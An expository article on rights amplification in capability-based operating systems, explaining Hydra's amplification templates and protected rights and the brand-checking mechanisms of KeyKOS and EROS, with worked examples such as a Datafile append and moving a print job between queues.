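# Rights amplification by design: Hydra, KeyKOS, sealer-unsealer pairs and AI agents

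## Capabilities, attenuation and the need for amplification

Rights amplification is a computer security technique in which a trusted program combines something it holds with something another program passes to it, and so gains access that neither gives alone. It belongs to capability-based systems, a family of operating systems, processors and programming languages that goes back to a 1966 paper by Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of the Massachusetts Institute of Technology. In these systems, a program can use only the objects it holds references to, and when it passes on a reference, it normally passes on the same rights or fewer. Designers introduced amplification in the early 1970s as a deliberate exception to this rule, so that ordinary programs, rather than a privileged core of the operating system, could provide services such as file storage. Engineers who deploy AI agents now face a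 related problem, because an agent may need to use a password that it should never be able to read.

A capability is an unforgeable reference to an object, together with rights to use that object. The object may be a stretch of memory, a file, a printer or a message port. Each right, recorded in the capability, permits one kind of operation on the object, such as reading or writing. Levy (1984), in *Capability- and Object-Based System Concepts*, gives the example of a program that adds a record to a file by calling the file system's PUT operation and supplying its capability for the file. The capability both identifies the file and determines whether the program may write to it.

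Mainstream operating systems mostly keep those two matters apart. A program names a file with a string of characters, and the system then looks up whether the user behind the program may touch that file. Miller and Shapiro (2003), in *Paradigm Regained*, show the cost with two Unix commands that do the same job. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` hands the copying program two names. Since those names could refer to any file at all, the program has to run with the user's full access to the file system. With `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the command shell opens both files first and passes the open files along, and the copying program needs nothing else. (Unix gives it the user's full access anyway.)

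None of this works if a program can write its own capabilities. Most early systems therefore kept them in a C-list, a list that only the operating system or the hardware could alter. The program referred to a capability by its position in the list. The main alternative was tagging. IBM's System/38 attached an extra bit to every 32-bit word so that the hardware could tell capabilities from ordinary data anywhere in memory. Levy's closing chapter, *Issues in Capability-Based Architectures*, reports that C-lists had dominated until then because they are simpler to build.

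### Sharing a file read-only

In Hydra, an operating system kernel from Carnegie-Mellon University, a program can give another program part of its access. *Protection in the Hydra Operating System* (Cohen and Jefferson, 1975) describes a program, User-1, that may read and write a file and wants a second program, User-2, only to read it. Both hold capabilities for a shared object used as a drop box. User-1 stores a copy of its file capability there with a mask. Hydra records the rights in a capability as 24 bits, one for each right, and the kernel keeps only the bits set in both the original and the mask. User-2 then picks up a capability that permits only reading the file.

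If *R* is the set of rights in the original and *M* the set that the mask lets through, the copy carries *R* ∩ *M*, which is never larger than *R*. The same holds for every later copy, so if User-2 passes the file to a third program, that program gets read access at most. Passing on a capability with fewer rights than one holds is called attenuation. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) describes a way to do this without bits and masks, in which an intermediary object holds the full capability, answers read requests and offers no other operation.

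Attenuation makes capability systems easy to reason about. Miller and Shapiro summarize the underlying rule as "only connectivity begets connectivity", meaning that all access derives from earlier access. An analyst can find the most that a program could ever reach by following the references outward from it, and two groups of objects with no reference between them will stay separate.

### What the file system needs and its clients must not have

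Hydra's designers intended the file system to be an ordinary program. In such a system, a file consists of disk blocks and a record of which blocks belong to it and in what order. A client needs something that proves its claim to the file, and a capability does that well. But if the capability also gives the client direct access to the blocks, the client can corrupt the record, or come to depend on a storage format that the file system's author later wants to change. Levy gives the example of a shared calendar. If a user gave a colleague a fully privileged capability to check for free afternoons, the colleague could also read every private entry directly from memory.

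So the client should get a weak capability. But when the client hands it back and asks the file system to write a record, the file system receives at most *R* ∩ *M* under the rule of attenuation, and those rights exclude access to the blocks. The file system must be able to open any file handed to it, yet it receives no more access than the client had.

A program in the file system's position is a type manager, which creates objects of one type and is the only program allowed to open their internal representation. Redell (1974), in *Naming and Protection in Extendible Operating Systems*, describes two ways to let the client and the manager use the same kind of capability. The manager can keep a table with a full-strength capability for every object it has made, and look up the right entry each time it receives a weak one. Redell calls this reasonable, if clumsy. Alternatively, the system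 can let the manager turn the weak capability back into a strong one, which is amplification.

Redell was wary of the second option. If a file system stores each file in a memory segment and gives the client a weakened capability for that segment, it needs the power to amplify capabilities for segments, and everyone else's private data is in segments too. The lower layer of software that supplies segments cannot distinguish an honest file system from a hostile program that asks for the same power. This is a strong objection to amplification on its own, but a weaker one to Hydra's version, in which "file" can be its own type and the power to amplify is specific to a type. According to *The Hydra System*, another of Levy's chapters, only a holder of the capability for the type itself can create amplification templates, the kernel-protected entries that confer this power. Redell grants that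 amplification combined with a second Hydra mechanism is as powerful as his preferred alternative, sealing one capability inside another.

### Two senses of the term

"Rights amplification" has two easily confused meanings in the literature. In Hydra, it means gaining more rights to the same object. For example, when a client passes a file capability that lacks the right to read the file's contents directly, the file system's procedure receives a capability for the same file with that right added.

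The other meaning is new access that comes from combining two references. Mark Miller, who had used the term for years in work on object-capability languages, defined it in a discussion on the Spritely Institute's forum, *"Rights Amplification" term alternate?*. Suppose holding *x* gives authority *X*, holding *y* gives authority *Y*, and someone combines them into *z*. In most useful combinations, *z* gives no more than the union of *X* and *Y*, and often less by design. Amplification is the special case in which *z* gives something outside that union. The usual example is a can and a can opener. In software, the standard form is a matched pair of objects called a sealer and an unsealer. The sealer closes a value in a box that only the unsealer can open, so holding both the box and the unsealer gives access to a reference that neither provides alone.

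Lemmer Webber (2020) points out in *Musing on the key metaphor* that a house key is a poor metaphor for a capability because the house's location is separate from the power to enter it. A person needs the address to find the door and the key to open it. Others in the exchange objected that the separation is not complete. Jonathan Shapiro noted that a key does designate its lock to the extent that its contour has to fit the pins, and Alan Karp noted that a parking valet ties a tag with the licence number to each car key. A tagged key is much closer to a capability because it carries designation and access together.

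The word "amplification" causes some of the confusion. A participant in the Spritely discussion observed that newcomers take it to mean giving a single capability more authority, which is wrong for sealing but nearly right for Hydra. In the same thread, Miller recalls that Norm Hardy, an architect of the KeyKOS operating system, preferred "synergy". The two senses overlap in practice. Cohen and Jefferson explain that other systems seal an object before giving it to a user, whereas in Hydra sealing just means removing the rights to the object's contents, and amplification does the unsealing. As with an unsealer, Hydra's procedure needs two things, the client's capability and its own template. But Hydra returns a stronger reference to an object the client had already named, while an unsealer can return a reference to something the client could not name at all.

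### Two ways to build a type manager

Levy's *Issues in Capability-Based Architectures* distinguishes two designs for type managers, only one of which needs amplification. The older capability machines used the other design.

In that design, the type manager creates a new protected instance of itself for each object. The Plessey System 250, a British industrial computer of 1969, and the CAP computer at the University of Cambridge both worked this way. When a client creates a file, it receives a capability for a new protected environment that contains the file system's procedures and the full-strength capability for that one file's blocks. The client's capability gives it only the right to enter, which means calling the public procedures. To write a record, the client calls the instance, which uses the strong capability it has had since its creation, so nothing has to turn a weak capability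 into a strong one. Redell adds that the design handles read-only sharing tolerably well, because the manager makes a second instance for the same file that is programmed never to write, and the two instances share nearly all their contents.

The weakness appears when one operation has to open two objects. The client selects a file by calling that file's instance, so each call concerns one file. Redell's counterexample is a file-to-file copy. The client calls file A's instance and passes its capability for file B, but A's instance gets only the right to enter B. It can send data to B through B's public procedures, one request at a time. It cannot open B's representation, which it would need to do to make both files share the same blocks. Operations that apply to no existing object, such as "create a file", or to a whole set, such as "close all open files", fit this design just as awkwardly.

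*Rights Amplification* (Brinkmann 2005), a proposal made with Neal Walfield for the L4 family of small operating-system kernels, describes a closely related difficulty. A memory server offers containers and an operation that copies data from container A to container B. The client sends its request to A and includes its capability for B. The server can identify A because the message arrived there, but it receives the capability for B only as an argument. Under the L4 design of the time, it had no way to match that capability to one of its own containers, even though it had created B itself. Brinkmann and Walfield proposed a kernel call that would trace the argument back through the programs that had passed it along until it reached the server's original reference.

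The other design Levy describes is restriction followed by amplification, which Hydra and Intel's iAPX 432 processor of 1981 adopted. One type manager serves all objects of its type. It returns restricted capabilities to clients and keeps a private capability that allows it to amplify any of them. Copying one file to another is then simple, because the client passes capabilities for both files as arguments and the manager amplifies both. An object's capability no longer leads to an instance of the manager, so clients need another way to reach it. They can hold a separate capability for the manager, or the system can find the manager from the object's type, as both Hydra and the 432 allow.

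The drawback of Hydra's design is that it concentrates risk in the file manager. A faulty manager endangers every file that anyone hands to it, whereas a faulty instance on the Plessey machine endangers only the file it was created with. A manager with Redell's table is riskier still, because it always has full access to all files, including those that no client has presented.

### Permission and authority

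Amplification changes what the type manager may do, and only indirectly what the client can achieve. Miller and Shapiro distinguish permission, which is what a program may do directly to the objects it can access, from authority, which also includes the effects it can bring about through other programs. If Alice has permission to read a file and regularly sends Bob copies of the text, Bob has authority to read the file but no permission to do so. Whether Bob keeps that authority depends on Alice's behavior as well as on who holds which references.

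Habitat Chronicles illustrates the difference between permission and authority with the Unix `passwd` command. An ordinary user has no permission to modify the system's password file but can run `passwd`, which has that permission. The user therefore has authority to change one password. The command also has permission to delete the file, but its code offers no such operation, so the user gains no authority to delete it.

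The file system's client is in the same position as that user. It never gets permission to touch the disk blocks, even while its own request is running. Amplification gives that permission to the type manager, and the manager's code determines how much of it becomes authority for the client, so a mistake in the code can give the client too much. A confused deputy is a program that is led to use its own authority for a requester who lacks it. Miller argues that in object-capability systems, confused deputies arise by accident only where there is amplification. He also concedes that "authority amplification" would have been a better name.

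### Five questions to ask of any design

Systems that amplify rights differ in five respects. A file system in the style of Hydra gives a first set of answers.

1. Who holds the amplifying authority? Here it is the type manager for files, and no client.
2. What does the client present? It presents a capability for the file, too weak to open the contents but impossible to forge.
3. What does the system check? It checks that the capability is for a file and carries the right that the requested operation requires. A client with a read-only capability should fail at this point if it asks to write.
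4. What does the type manager gain, and for how long? It gains access to the contents of that one file. The kernel discards a procedure's working C-list when the call returns, so the access ends there unless the procedure has stored the stronger capability somewhere else.
5. What can someone audit afterwards? Capability systems start at a disadvantage here, because programs copy capabilities freely and, as Levy notes, it is hard in most of them to find out who has access to an object. Habitat Chronicles replies that access lists are little better, since people share passwords, and suggests handing out an intermediary object that records who received the access and why. A type manager can keep a log too, as every operation on a file's contents goes through it, but a bare capability shows only that the caller holds it and not how the caller came by it.

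## Hydra: procedures that receive more rights than their callers

Hydra ran on C.mmp, a computer that Carnegie-Mellon assembled in the 1970s from up to 16 minicomputers and a large shared memory. Hydra's kernel did not include a file system, directories or a command language, so that users could write these as ordinary programs and run several versions of each side by side. In *HYDRA/C.mmp*, their 1981 book about the project, Wulf, Levin and Harbison call amplification crucial to this goal.

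*HYDRA* (Wulf, Cohen and colleagues, 1974), an early account of the kernel, compares the arrangement to telephone repair. Customers may not repair their own telephones, but they can call a repairman. He has a general right to repair telephones, but he cannot work on a particular one until the customer lets him in. In Hydra, the general right corresponds to an amplification template, and letting the repairman in corresponds to passing a capability as an argument.

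### Objects and their 24 rights

Hydra treats everything as an object, including files, running programs and types. Each object has a name, a type and a representation. The name is a 64-bit number that the system never reuses, and knowing it gives no access to the object. The type is the name of another object, the type object, which represents the whole class of objects of that type. Users add a new kind of resource by creating a new type object.

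An object's representation has a data part, which holds ordinary memory words, and a C-list, which holds capabilities. The two are separate because the PDP-11 processors in C.mmp could not tag capabilities in memory. Any Hydra object can have a C-list, whereas in many other capability systems of the time only a running program had one. A programmer can therefore build a directory out of capabilities for files, or a file out of capabilities for pages of memory. A program that can open one object may then be able to reach many others.

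Of the 24 rights in a capability, 16 are generic, which means that they have the same meaning for every type. Nine of these control basic operations:

- reading, overwriting and extending the data part
- loading, storing, appending and deleting capabilities in the C-list
- copying or destroying the whole object

Most of the other generic rights limit what can happen to an object or capability later. Two of them, the modify right and the environment right, are important for amplification.

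The remaining eight rights are auxiliary, and each type's designer decides what they mean. The kernel compares the bits without interpreting them. In one of the book's examples, a file system offers read, write and update operations. Its designer can give each operation its own bit, or use two bits and require both for an update.

A file system gives its clients a weak capability, which typically carries some auxiliary rights but none of the generic rights that allow access to a file's representation.

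### A new environment for each call

A procedure is also an object. Its C-list holds the capabilities it needs on every call, such as those for its code and private data, along with placeholders for the arguments. When a program calls the procedure, the kernel creates another object, the local name space, which serves as the C-list of the running code. The kernel copies the procedure's own capabilities into this object and fills the placeholders with capabilities from the caller.

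The running code can use the capabilities in its local name space and any it can reach through them. To reach one indirectly, it gives the kernel a path, such as "the third capability in the object that the second capability refers to". At each step, the kernel checks that the program has the right to load capabilities from that object. The procedure can use nothing else that belongs to the caller, and the caller cannot see the procedure's private capabilities. A user can therefore run a stranger's program on one file without exposing other files, and the stranger can offer the program without giving users access to its data.

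Many calls in Hydra pass a capability across this boundary with its rights unchanged or reduced. A call can also amplify those rights there, and a template determines whether it does.

### Three kinds of template

A template is an entry in a C-list that refers to a type instead of a particular object. Hydra has three kinds.

A **creation template** contains a type and a set of rights. Its holder can create objects of that type and receives a capability with those rights for each one. A subsystem, Hydra's term for the procedures that together implement a type, can remove the rights to the representation from a template and then give the template to anyone. If new objects need careful initialization, the subsystem can instead keep the template and offer a procedure that creates the objects.

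A **parameter template** contains a type and a set of required rights, and only checks that an argument has them. Subsystems can hand out these templates freely, so anyone can write a procedure that accepts, say, a file with the read right.

An **amplification template** contains a type, a set of required rights and a set of new rights. Hydra checks that the caller's capability has that type and the required rights, then gives the procedure the new rights to the object. Cohen and Jefferson expect that no subsystem will ever make its amplification templates generally available, and the kernel never gives out templates of this kind for its own types, such as processes.

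All three kinds of template come from the capability for the type object, provided that it includes a special right to make templates. The book gives the example of a small subsystem for Boxes, objects that each hold a single capability. Two procedures, Deposit and Withdraw, put a capability in a Box or take it out. A set-up program creates the type and gives the builder a parameter template, a restricted creation template and a capability for the type object. The builder can publish both templates, but anyone who obtained the capability for the type object could make a new amplification template, or copy an existing one out of Deposit's C-list, and then open every Box in the system. Wulf and colleagues suggest that the builder keep this capability in a private catalogue, and they acknowledge that the Boxes are then only as secure as the catalogue program.

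### What the kernel does with an argument

A call with an amplified argument goes through five steps.

1. The caller names the procedure and supplies a capability and a mask for each argument. The mask works as it does when users share a file, so the caller passes the rights *C* = *R* ∩ *M*.
2. The kernel creates a local name space and copies the procedure's own capabilities into it.
3. When it comes to a template, the kernel takes the next argument and checks that the object has the right type and that *C* includes all the required rights, *Q*. If any argument fails, the kernel destroys the local name space and reports an error to the caller.
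4. For a parameter template, the kernel stores the argument with the rights *C*. For an amplification template, it stores a capability for the same object with the new rights, *N*, except for certain protected rights that the caller did not pass.
5. The procedure runs. When it returns, the kernel destroys the local name space, along with every capability in it, and the caller continues in its old environment. The procedure can hand back one capability as a result.

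The caller's own capability stays as it was throughout. If *P* is the set of protected rights, an amplified call succeeds when the type matches and *Q* ⊆ *C*, and the procedure receives

(*N* − *P*) ∪ (*N* ∩ *P* ∩ *C*).

The first part consists of the ordinary new rights, which the procedure gets whether or not the caller had them. The second part consists of protected rights, which the procedure gets only if both the template and the caller supply them. (The formula leaves out one detail in the book's version, where the kernel always adds the right to delete the new capability from its list.)

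Rights the caller passed disappear unless the template lists them among the new rights. Amplification in Hydra is therefore closer to replacing rights than to adding them. Wulf and colleagues note in their 1974 paper that the procedure's rights may be a superset of the caller's, a subset, or a completely different set.

### Appending to a Datafile

Cohen and Jefferson illustrate the mechanism with a type called Datafile, a file whose C-list contains capabilities for Data objects, the kernel's simplest containers. The procedure Datafile-Append takes a Datafile and a Data object and adds the Data object's contents to the end of the Datafile. Its C-list has three entries: a capability for its code, a parameter template for the Data object and an amplification template for the Datafile. The amplification template requires auxiliary right 2. The kernel does not define what that right means, but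 it serves as the right to append to a Datafile because Datafile-Append requires it.

Suppose that a user may read and append to a Datafile, and wants to be sure that the procedure cannot keep any access afterwards. The user masks out the environment right, which a program needs in order to store a capability outside its local name space, and the read right, which this call does not need. The rights might then look like this, with 1 for present and 0 for absent:

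| Right to the Datafile | Caller holds (*R*) | Mask (*M*) | Passed (*C*) | Required (*Q*) | New (*N*) | Procedure receives |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Load capabilities from C-list | 0 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| Append capabilities to C-list | 0 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| Modify (protected) | 1 | 1 | 1 | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| Environment (protected) | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 1 | 0 |
| Auxiliary 2: append to Datafile | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 0 | 0 |
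| Auxiliary 5: read Datafile | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The only required right is present, so the call succeeds. The procedure gains the rights to load and append capabilities, which the caller lacked. It keeps the modify right because the caller passed it, but it does not get the environment right, although the template lists it. It also does not get auxiliary right 2, which was needed only to make the call.

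The procedure can now read the text in the Data object, copy it into a new Data object and append a capability for that object to the Datafile's C-list. If a user who could only read the Datafile made the same call, the kernel would reject it at the third step, before any of the subsystem's code ran, so a mistake in Datafile-Append's code could not let that user append.

If the caller had also masked out the modify right, the call would still have begun, because *Q* does not include that right. The kernel would have refused the change when the procedure tried to make it. A careful author puts such rights in *Q*. The Box templates, for example, require the modify, environment and unconfined rights in addition to the auxiliary right for depositing or withdrawing.

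### Rights that amplification cannot restore

The protected rights exist because subsystems have bugs. Cohen and Jefferson imagine a user who urgently needs a printed listing of a Datafile that took a long time to construct. Just before calling Datafile-List, the user hears that a new bug may cause the procedure to erase the file. The user can't safely make a copy first, because Datafile-Copy belongs to the same subsystem and may have the same bug.

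Removing the rights to write to a file before passing it, as in ordinary attenuation, would not be enough to protect it, because an amplification template could restore them. Hydra therefore requires two rights for any change to an object: the right for the particular operation, such as appending a capability, and the general modify right. Amplification can supply the first but not the second. If the user removes the modify right, Datafile-List can open the Datafile and read it, but the kernel rejects every attempt to change it.

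The same restriction has to cover the Data objects inside the file, or the buggy procedure could erase those instead. When a program loads a capability through another capability that lacks the modify right, the kernel removes the modify right from the loaded one too. This protects even parts of the file that the user may not know exist. The protection fails only if Datafile-List already has its own capability for the file that includes the modify right.

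This protection also limits what the subsystem can do. Compacting or reorganizing the file before printing it might make later calls run faster, but without the modify right Datafile-List can reorganize only a copy. The subsystem's designer could instead put the modify right in *Q* and turn away callers who withhold it. Callers must then decide whether they trust the subsystem enough to grant that right.

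This affected the file system that Hydra's users built. Its procedure for opening a file normally records the date of last access, which changes the file. If the caller's capability lacks the modify right, the procedure skips this step. Even locking a file briefly to prevent conflicts would have been a problem, because operating a lock counts as a modification. The file system was therefore designed so that readers need only one capability from the file, which the kernel can copy in a single indivisible operation without a lock.

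The environment right controls how long the procedure can keep its added rights. If the caller leaves it in place and the template also lists it, the procedure can save its strengthened capability in a private object and use it long after returning. If the caller removes it, the procedure can still pass the capability to other procedures it calls, but the kernel erases every copy as those calls return. Cohen and Jefferson also say this right can help assign responsibility. If one user shares an object with a second and withholds the environment right, the second cannot give a third user lasting access. When something odd happens to the object, the first user knows whom to ask. This is a weak form of auditing because it narrows down the suspects but doesn't record what anyone did.

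Neither right stops a procedure from copying a file's text into another object that a spy can read. Hydra uses the unconfined right to control this. If a caller invokes a procedure through a capability that lacks the unconfined right, the kernel removes the modify right from everything the procedure brings along. A tax program called this way can fill in the customer's form but cannot write the customer's income anywhere else that would survive the call. Some information could still escape through side effects such as patterns of memory use. Amplification cannot restore the unconfined right either.

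The 1975 paper describes one more protected right, which marks an object as frozen, meaning its contents can never change. The presence of this right is a guarantee to other users, so a template that could add it would let a subsystem make false guarantees. Freezing was planned but not yet implemented when the paper appeared.

### Finding the procedure through the object

In an ordinary Hydra call, the client needs one capability for the object and another for the procedure. TYPECALL removes the need for the second. The C-list of a type object contains capabilities for the subsystem's procedures, each at a known position. To send a message to a port, for example, a client presents its capability for the port and asks for the procedure at position 2. The kernel finds the port's type object, takes the procedure from that position and calls it. The client usually names the port twice, once to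 find the procedure and once as the argument whose rights are to be amplified.

The client never receives a capability for the type object, so TYPECALL does not give it the power to make templates. TYPECALL also lets a program work with objects without identifying their type. If every subsystem puts its "report your status" procedure at the same position, one command can report the status of files, locks and everything else. Hydra had two directory systems with matching sets of procedures, and the command interpreter could use either without checking which it had.

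With TYPECALL, withholding the capability for a procedure would no longer protect an object, so protection would depend entirely on auxiliary rights. In an example from the 1974 paper, a researcher creates a type for annotated bibliographies, with procedures to update a bibliography, print it, print it without the annotations, and erase it. Each procedure requires its own auxiliary right. One colleague has the erase right for a bibliography but no capability for the erase procedure, so the right is useless. With TYPECALL, the same colleague could reach the procedure through the bibliography itself, as long as the type object listed it.

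The designers first saw TYPECALL as a convenience that saved them from handing out many procedure capabilities. By 1981, Wulf and colleagues considered it essential and thought a successor to Hydra might not need the ordinary call.

### Does amplification breach security?

Hydra guarantees callers tight control over what a procedure can do with their objects, and amplification is an exception to that guarantee. Cohen and Jefferson give two reasons not to regard it as a genuine breach. First, amplification gives a procedure new rights only to objects that the caller passed, so any damage is limited to those objects. Second, a procedure with an amplification template for a type is by definition part of that type's subsystem, and someone who does not trust the subsystem should not use the type.

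The first reason is correct about what the kernel puts into the local name space, but the procedure can reach other objects from there. Subsystems often need the right to load capabilities from an object's C-list. The 1974 paper calls a similar right the "walk right" and says it is among those most commonly amplified. Suppose a user passes a directory to a procedure that looks up a single file. With the load right, the procedure can take out the capability for every file in the directory, with whatever rights the directory holds. If some entries are directories too, the procedure may be able to open those as well. The kernel offers the template check as a separate operation, called Merge, so a procedure that keeps an amplification template among its private objects could apply it to each subdirectory in turn and reach everything in the tree.

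The same paper gives a more accurate limit elsewhere, saying that even a malicious procedure can damage only objects reachable through the parameters. This still protects the caller's other files unless the directory leads to them. But an analyst has to work out what is reachable using the procedure's amplified rights, not the caller's. The caller also can't easily judge the risk, because a user without the load right cannot inspect the directory's C-list and has to rely on the subsystem to describe its contents.

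The second reason depends on how subsystems behave, because the holder of the type capability can give copies of an amplification template to others. Cohen and Jefferson describe one result. They planned to let a user share an object through an alias, an intermediate link that the user could later break. A procedure that amplified a capability for the alias would receive a capability for the object itself, so that revocation could not interrupt an update halfway and leave the object inconsistent. If a careless or hostile subsystem gave its amplification template to ordinary users, they could exchange their aliases for direct capabilities, which revocation would not affect. Aliases were unfinished in 1975, and the 1981 book says that Hydra's mechanisms do not address revocation.

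Both reasons concern the caller, who chooses to pass the object and to trust the subsystem. In the bibliography example, the person at risk may instead be the researcher, who lets a colleague print a bibliography without its annotations, some of which comment on that colleague's work. When the colleague calls the procedure, the procedure gains access to the whole file, including the annotations, and only its code keeps them out of the printout.

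The argument is therefore sound for a subsystem that works correctly and does not share its templates. The modify and environment rights limit the harm in some cases where a subsystem does not meet both conditions, and their existence suggests that the designers did not think trust was entirely sufficient.

### What Hydra cost to use

*The Hydra System* reports that changing from one protection environment to another took over 35 milliseconds. Amplification was a negligible part of this, since checking and replacing rights takes only a few operations on strings of bits. The time went into building a local name space for every call, in software, on processors with no support for capabilities. The protected rights made calls somewhat slower still. Because a caller could have the kernel strip rights from a procedure's own capabilities, the kernel had to copy those capabilities afresh for each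 call, which ruled out some obvious shortcuts.

The designers had hoped that even small subroutines would run in their own environment, with only the access they needed. But each call took 35 milliseconds, so programmers used Hydra procedures only when they had to protect the caller or the supplier, or when the code was so large that the delay hardly mattered, as with a compiler.

Measurements of the file system show how heavy the burden could be. In one series of calls, the file system's own code took 49 milliseconds on average and the call mechanism took 89, or about 65% of the total. (Opening a file involves at least two calls, one to the main file system and one to the part that manages the data format, which may explain why the figure is so much higher than 35. The designers later improved these times somewhat.)

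The file system therefore avoided a procedure call for each read or write. A user called a procedure to open a file, and the kernel checked the user's rights at that point. The file system then connected the user to a server process, and all reading and writing took place through messages until the user closed the file. This was much faster, but the kernel checked rights against the template only when the session began, rather than on every append as in the Datafile example.

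Hydra showed that ordinary programmers could build such services outside the kernel. In May and June of 1976, six people designed the file system and its first data formats in a total of about 14 person-days, and each component took less than a person-month to implement. Users also wrote directory systems, text editors, command languages, and the software that connected C.mmp to the ARPANET, the forerunner of the internet. But few programmers at Carnegie-Mellon chose to work on Hydra. Wulf and colleagues admit that they were so taken with the protection mechanisms that they neglected the user interface and told themselves any user could easily build one.

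*The Hydra System* reports that the designers thought they had probably made their protection scheme too flexible. The 1981 book largely supports this with more specific complaints, including that Hydra had "too many rights". In practice, a subsystem gave a client either complete access to an object's representation or none, so one right could have replaced the seven that controlled the C-list and the data part. The new-rights field of the amplification template was also more precise than anyone needed. Most programmers who wrote subsystem procedures gave themselves all rights, because that was easier than working out which ones they required. The designers doubted that this did much harm, because users had to trust the subsystem anyway. A later system, StarOS, granted all rights automatically, and Hydra's designers said they would probably do the same.

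The book is less consistent on the protected rights. One chapter says that the environment and unconfined rights were probably not worth the bother and that a single right could have covered the common cases. Another defends the mechanisms on the grounds that important subsystems, including the file system, used them, but concedes that programmers rarely used the more advanced ones except as experiments. That chapter also says the mechanisms are not flexible enough. For example, a user who withholds the modify right for a directory also loses the ability to change any file reached through it, and Hydra has no way to protect the directory alone.

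Programmers regularly used basic rights checking and amplification. Wulf and colleagues attribute this more to a desire for well-structured programs than to concern about security, since few people in their research environment wanted restrictive policies.

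## KeyKOS and EROS: recognising one's own objects by brand

Hydra's kernel amplifies rights as part of a procedure call. KeyKOS, a commercial operating system that entered production in January 1983, provides amplification as a separate operation, which a program invokes when it needs to open an object it made earlier. Tymshare, which sold computer time over a network, began work on the system in 1975. According to *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture*, by Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues, Tymshare wanted precise accounting, round-the-clock service and enough security to let customers who distrusted each other share one machine.

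### Keys, nodes and domains

KeyKOS calls its capabilities keys. *KeyKOS Architecture* (Hardy, 1990) describes two basic kinds of storage: pages, which hold 4,096 bytes of data, and nodes, which have 16 slots that each hold one key. Only the kernel handles the bits that make up a key, so programs refer to their keys by slot.

A domain is roughly what other systems call a process. It combines a program with memory and the keys the program may use. Programmers normally use one domain for each object they want to provide. The domain lasts as long as the object does and sits idle between requests. The kernel saves the whole system to disk every few minutes, so domains and keys survive a power failure.

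In the original implementation, a domain consisted of three nodes. One stored the processor's registers and another stored the program's keys. The third, the root node, held what the kernel needed to run the domain, such as the key for its memory. Several types of key can refer to the same root node, and each type gives its holder different powers:

| Key | What the holder can do | Usual holder |
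|---|---|---|
| Start key | Send the domain a message, which the domain's own program interprets | Clients |
| Domain key | Read and replace the domain's registers, memory and working keys | The program that manages the object |
| Node key | Read or replace the contents of any slot in the root node | The program that builds the domain |

Hardy calls the domain key a "domain service key". A start key reveals nothing about the domain's code or data. The holder of a domain key can easily get a start key from it, which is ordinary attenuation, but getting a domain key from a start key requires a brand.

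### How a domain creator marks its domains

Programs get new domains from a domain creator. Each domain creator has a unique key of its own, which it uses as its brand. To make a domain:

1. A program calls the creator and supplies a key to a space bank, the service that allocates pages and nodes.
2. The creator gets nodes from the bank, assembles them into a domain and stores its brand in a special slot of the root node.
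3. The creator returns a domain key to the caller.
4. The caller uses this key to install a program, some memory and an allowance of processor time. It then obtains a start key and gives that to clients.

Months later, the same caller may receive a start key in a message and need to open the domain behind it:

1. The caller passes the start key to its domain creator.
2. The creator passes the start key and its brand to the domain tool, a kernel object that only domain creators can use.
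3. The kernel compares this brand with the one in the domain's root node.
4. If they match, the domain tool returns a node key for the root. The creator can exchange this for a domain key, also through the domain tool, and it gives the domain key to the caller.
5. If they differ, the caller gets no stronger key and still has only the start key.

Hardy calls the domain tool's comparison the primitive rights amplification mechanism of KeyKOS. The start key by itself only lets its holder send messages to the domain, and the brand gives no access without it. The kernel reads the brand directly from the domain's root node, so the check works even if the program inside is hostile or has crashed.

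EROS, a later system that Jonathan Shapiro and others built at the University of Pennsylvania, has a similar operation. *Capability authentication* (Shapiro, 2005) calls it `identify` and places it in a kernel capability named ProcessTool. The operation takes an entry capability (the EROS counterpart of a start key) and a brand, and returns only true or false. Programs called constructors hold the ProcessTool, and each constructor brands the processes it creates. Anyone who has a capability for a constructor can use it to check whether that constructor made a particular process.

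A KeyKOS domain creator hands over full control of any domain it recognises, so the creator's owner must keep its key private. An EROS constructor can safely offer the same check to the public, because a client that receives "true" learns where the process came from but gains no control over it.

### Moving a job between two queues

Suppose a printing service uses one domain for each print queue. A manager program has the only key to the service's domain creator. When the manager creates a queue, it gives out a start key and discards the domain key, so it does not need to keep the table of full-strength capabilities that Redell found clumsy.

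An operator has start keys for queues A and B and wants to move a waiting job from A to B. The operator should not be able to read the document. If A simply handed over the job's key for the operator to pass on to B, the operator could use that key to open the document on the way. The manager can avoid this:

1. The operator's program calls the manager with a request to move job 3 and includes the start keys for A and B. A KeyKOS message has room for four keys. In a call, the kernel uses the last of these for a resume key, through which the manager will reply, so both start keys fit.
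2. The manager passes A's start key to its domain creator and receives A's domain key. It does the same for B.
3. The manager copies the key for job 3 from A's slots to B's and clears the slot in A.
4. The manager discards both domain keys and replies to the operator.

Unlike the separate instances on the Plessey machine, one KeyKOS program can open both queues, and the job's key never reaches the operator.

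A message sent through a start key waits until the domain is free, but a domain key takes effect immediately, so the manager must still make sure that neither queue is halfway through another request. It should also check that the operator did not send the same queue twice. It could do this by comparing the two domain keys with Discrim, a KeyKOS kernel object that tests whether two keys are equal.

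A matching brand shows that A and B are genuine queues, but not that this operator may move jobs between them. Each KeyKOS start key carries an 8-bit number, chosen by whoever issues the key, for distinguishing clients. The domain receives this number with every message sent through the key, so a queue could use it to let some clients add jobs and others only view the list. But the brand comparison ignores the number, so a start key meant only for viewing would also pass. Hydra's template would have required a specific right before the procedure ran. In KeyKOS, whoever writes the manager has to add an equivalent check, for example by giving operators a start key to the manager itself with its own number.

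### What a forged object achieves

An attacker who wants to read other people's documents could write a program that behaves exactly like a print queue and put that program's start key in the request instead of B's. The attacker has no access to the service's domain creator, so the imitation has a different brand. The manager therefore gets no domain key for it and can refuse the request.

The forgery would succeed only if the manager's author had left out the brand check. The manager would then send the job to B in a message, giving the attacker the key to the document. The kernel does not force a program to check an argument's brand before using it.

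Stealing the brand is a more serious attack. Someone who had it could put it on an impostor, if they also had a node key for the impostor's root. In KeyKOS, keeping the brand secret depends partly on the space bank, although Shapiro describes the brand as impossible to disclose. The caller chooses the bank that supplies the nodes for a new domain. If that bank kept a node key for the root, the bank's owner could read the brand out of its slot. Official banks prevent this by giving out each node only once, so no stranger has another key to it. A domain creator therefore needs assurance that the bank is official.

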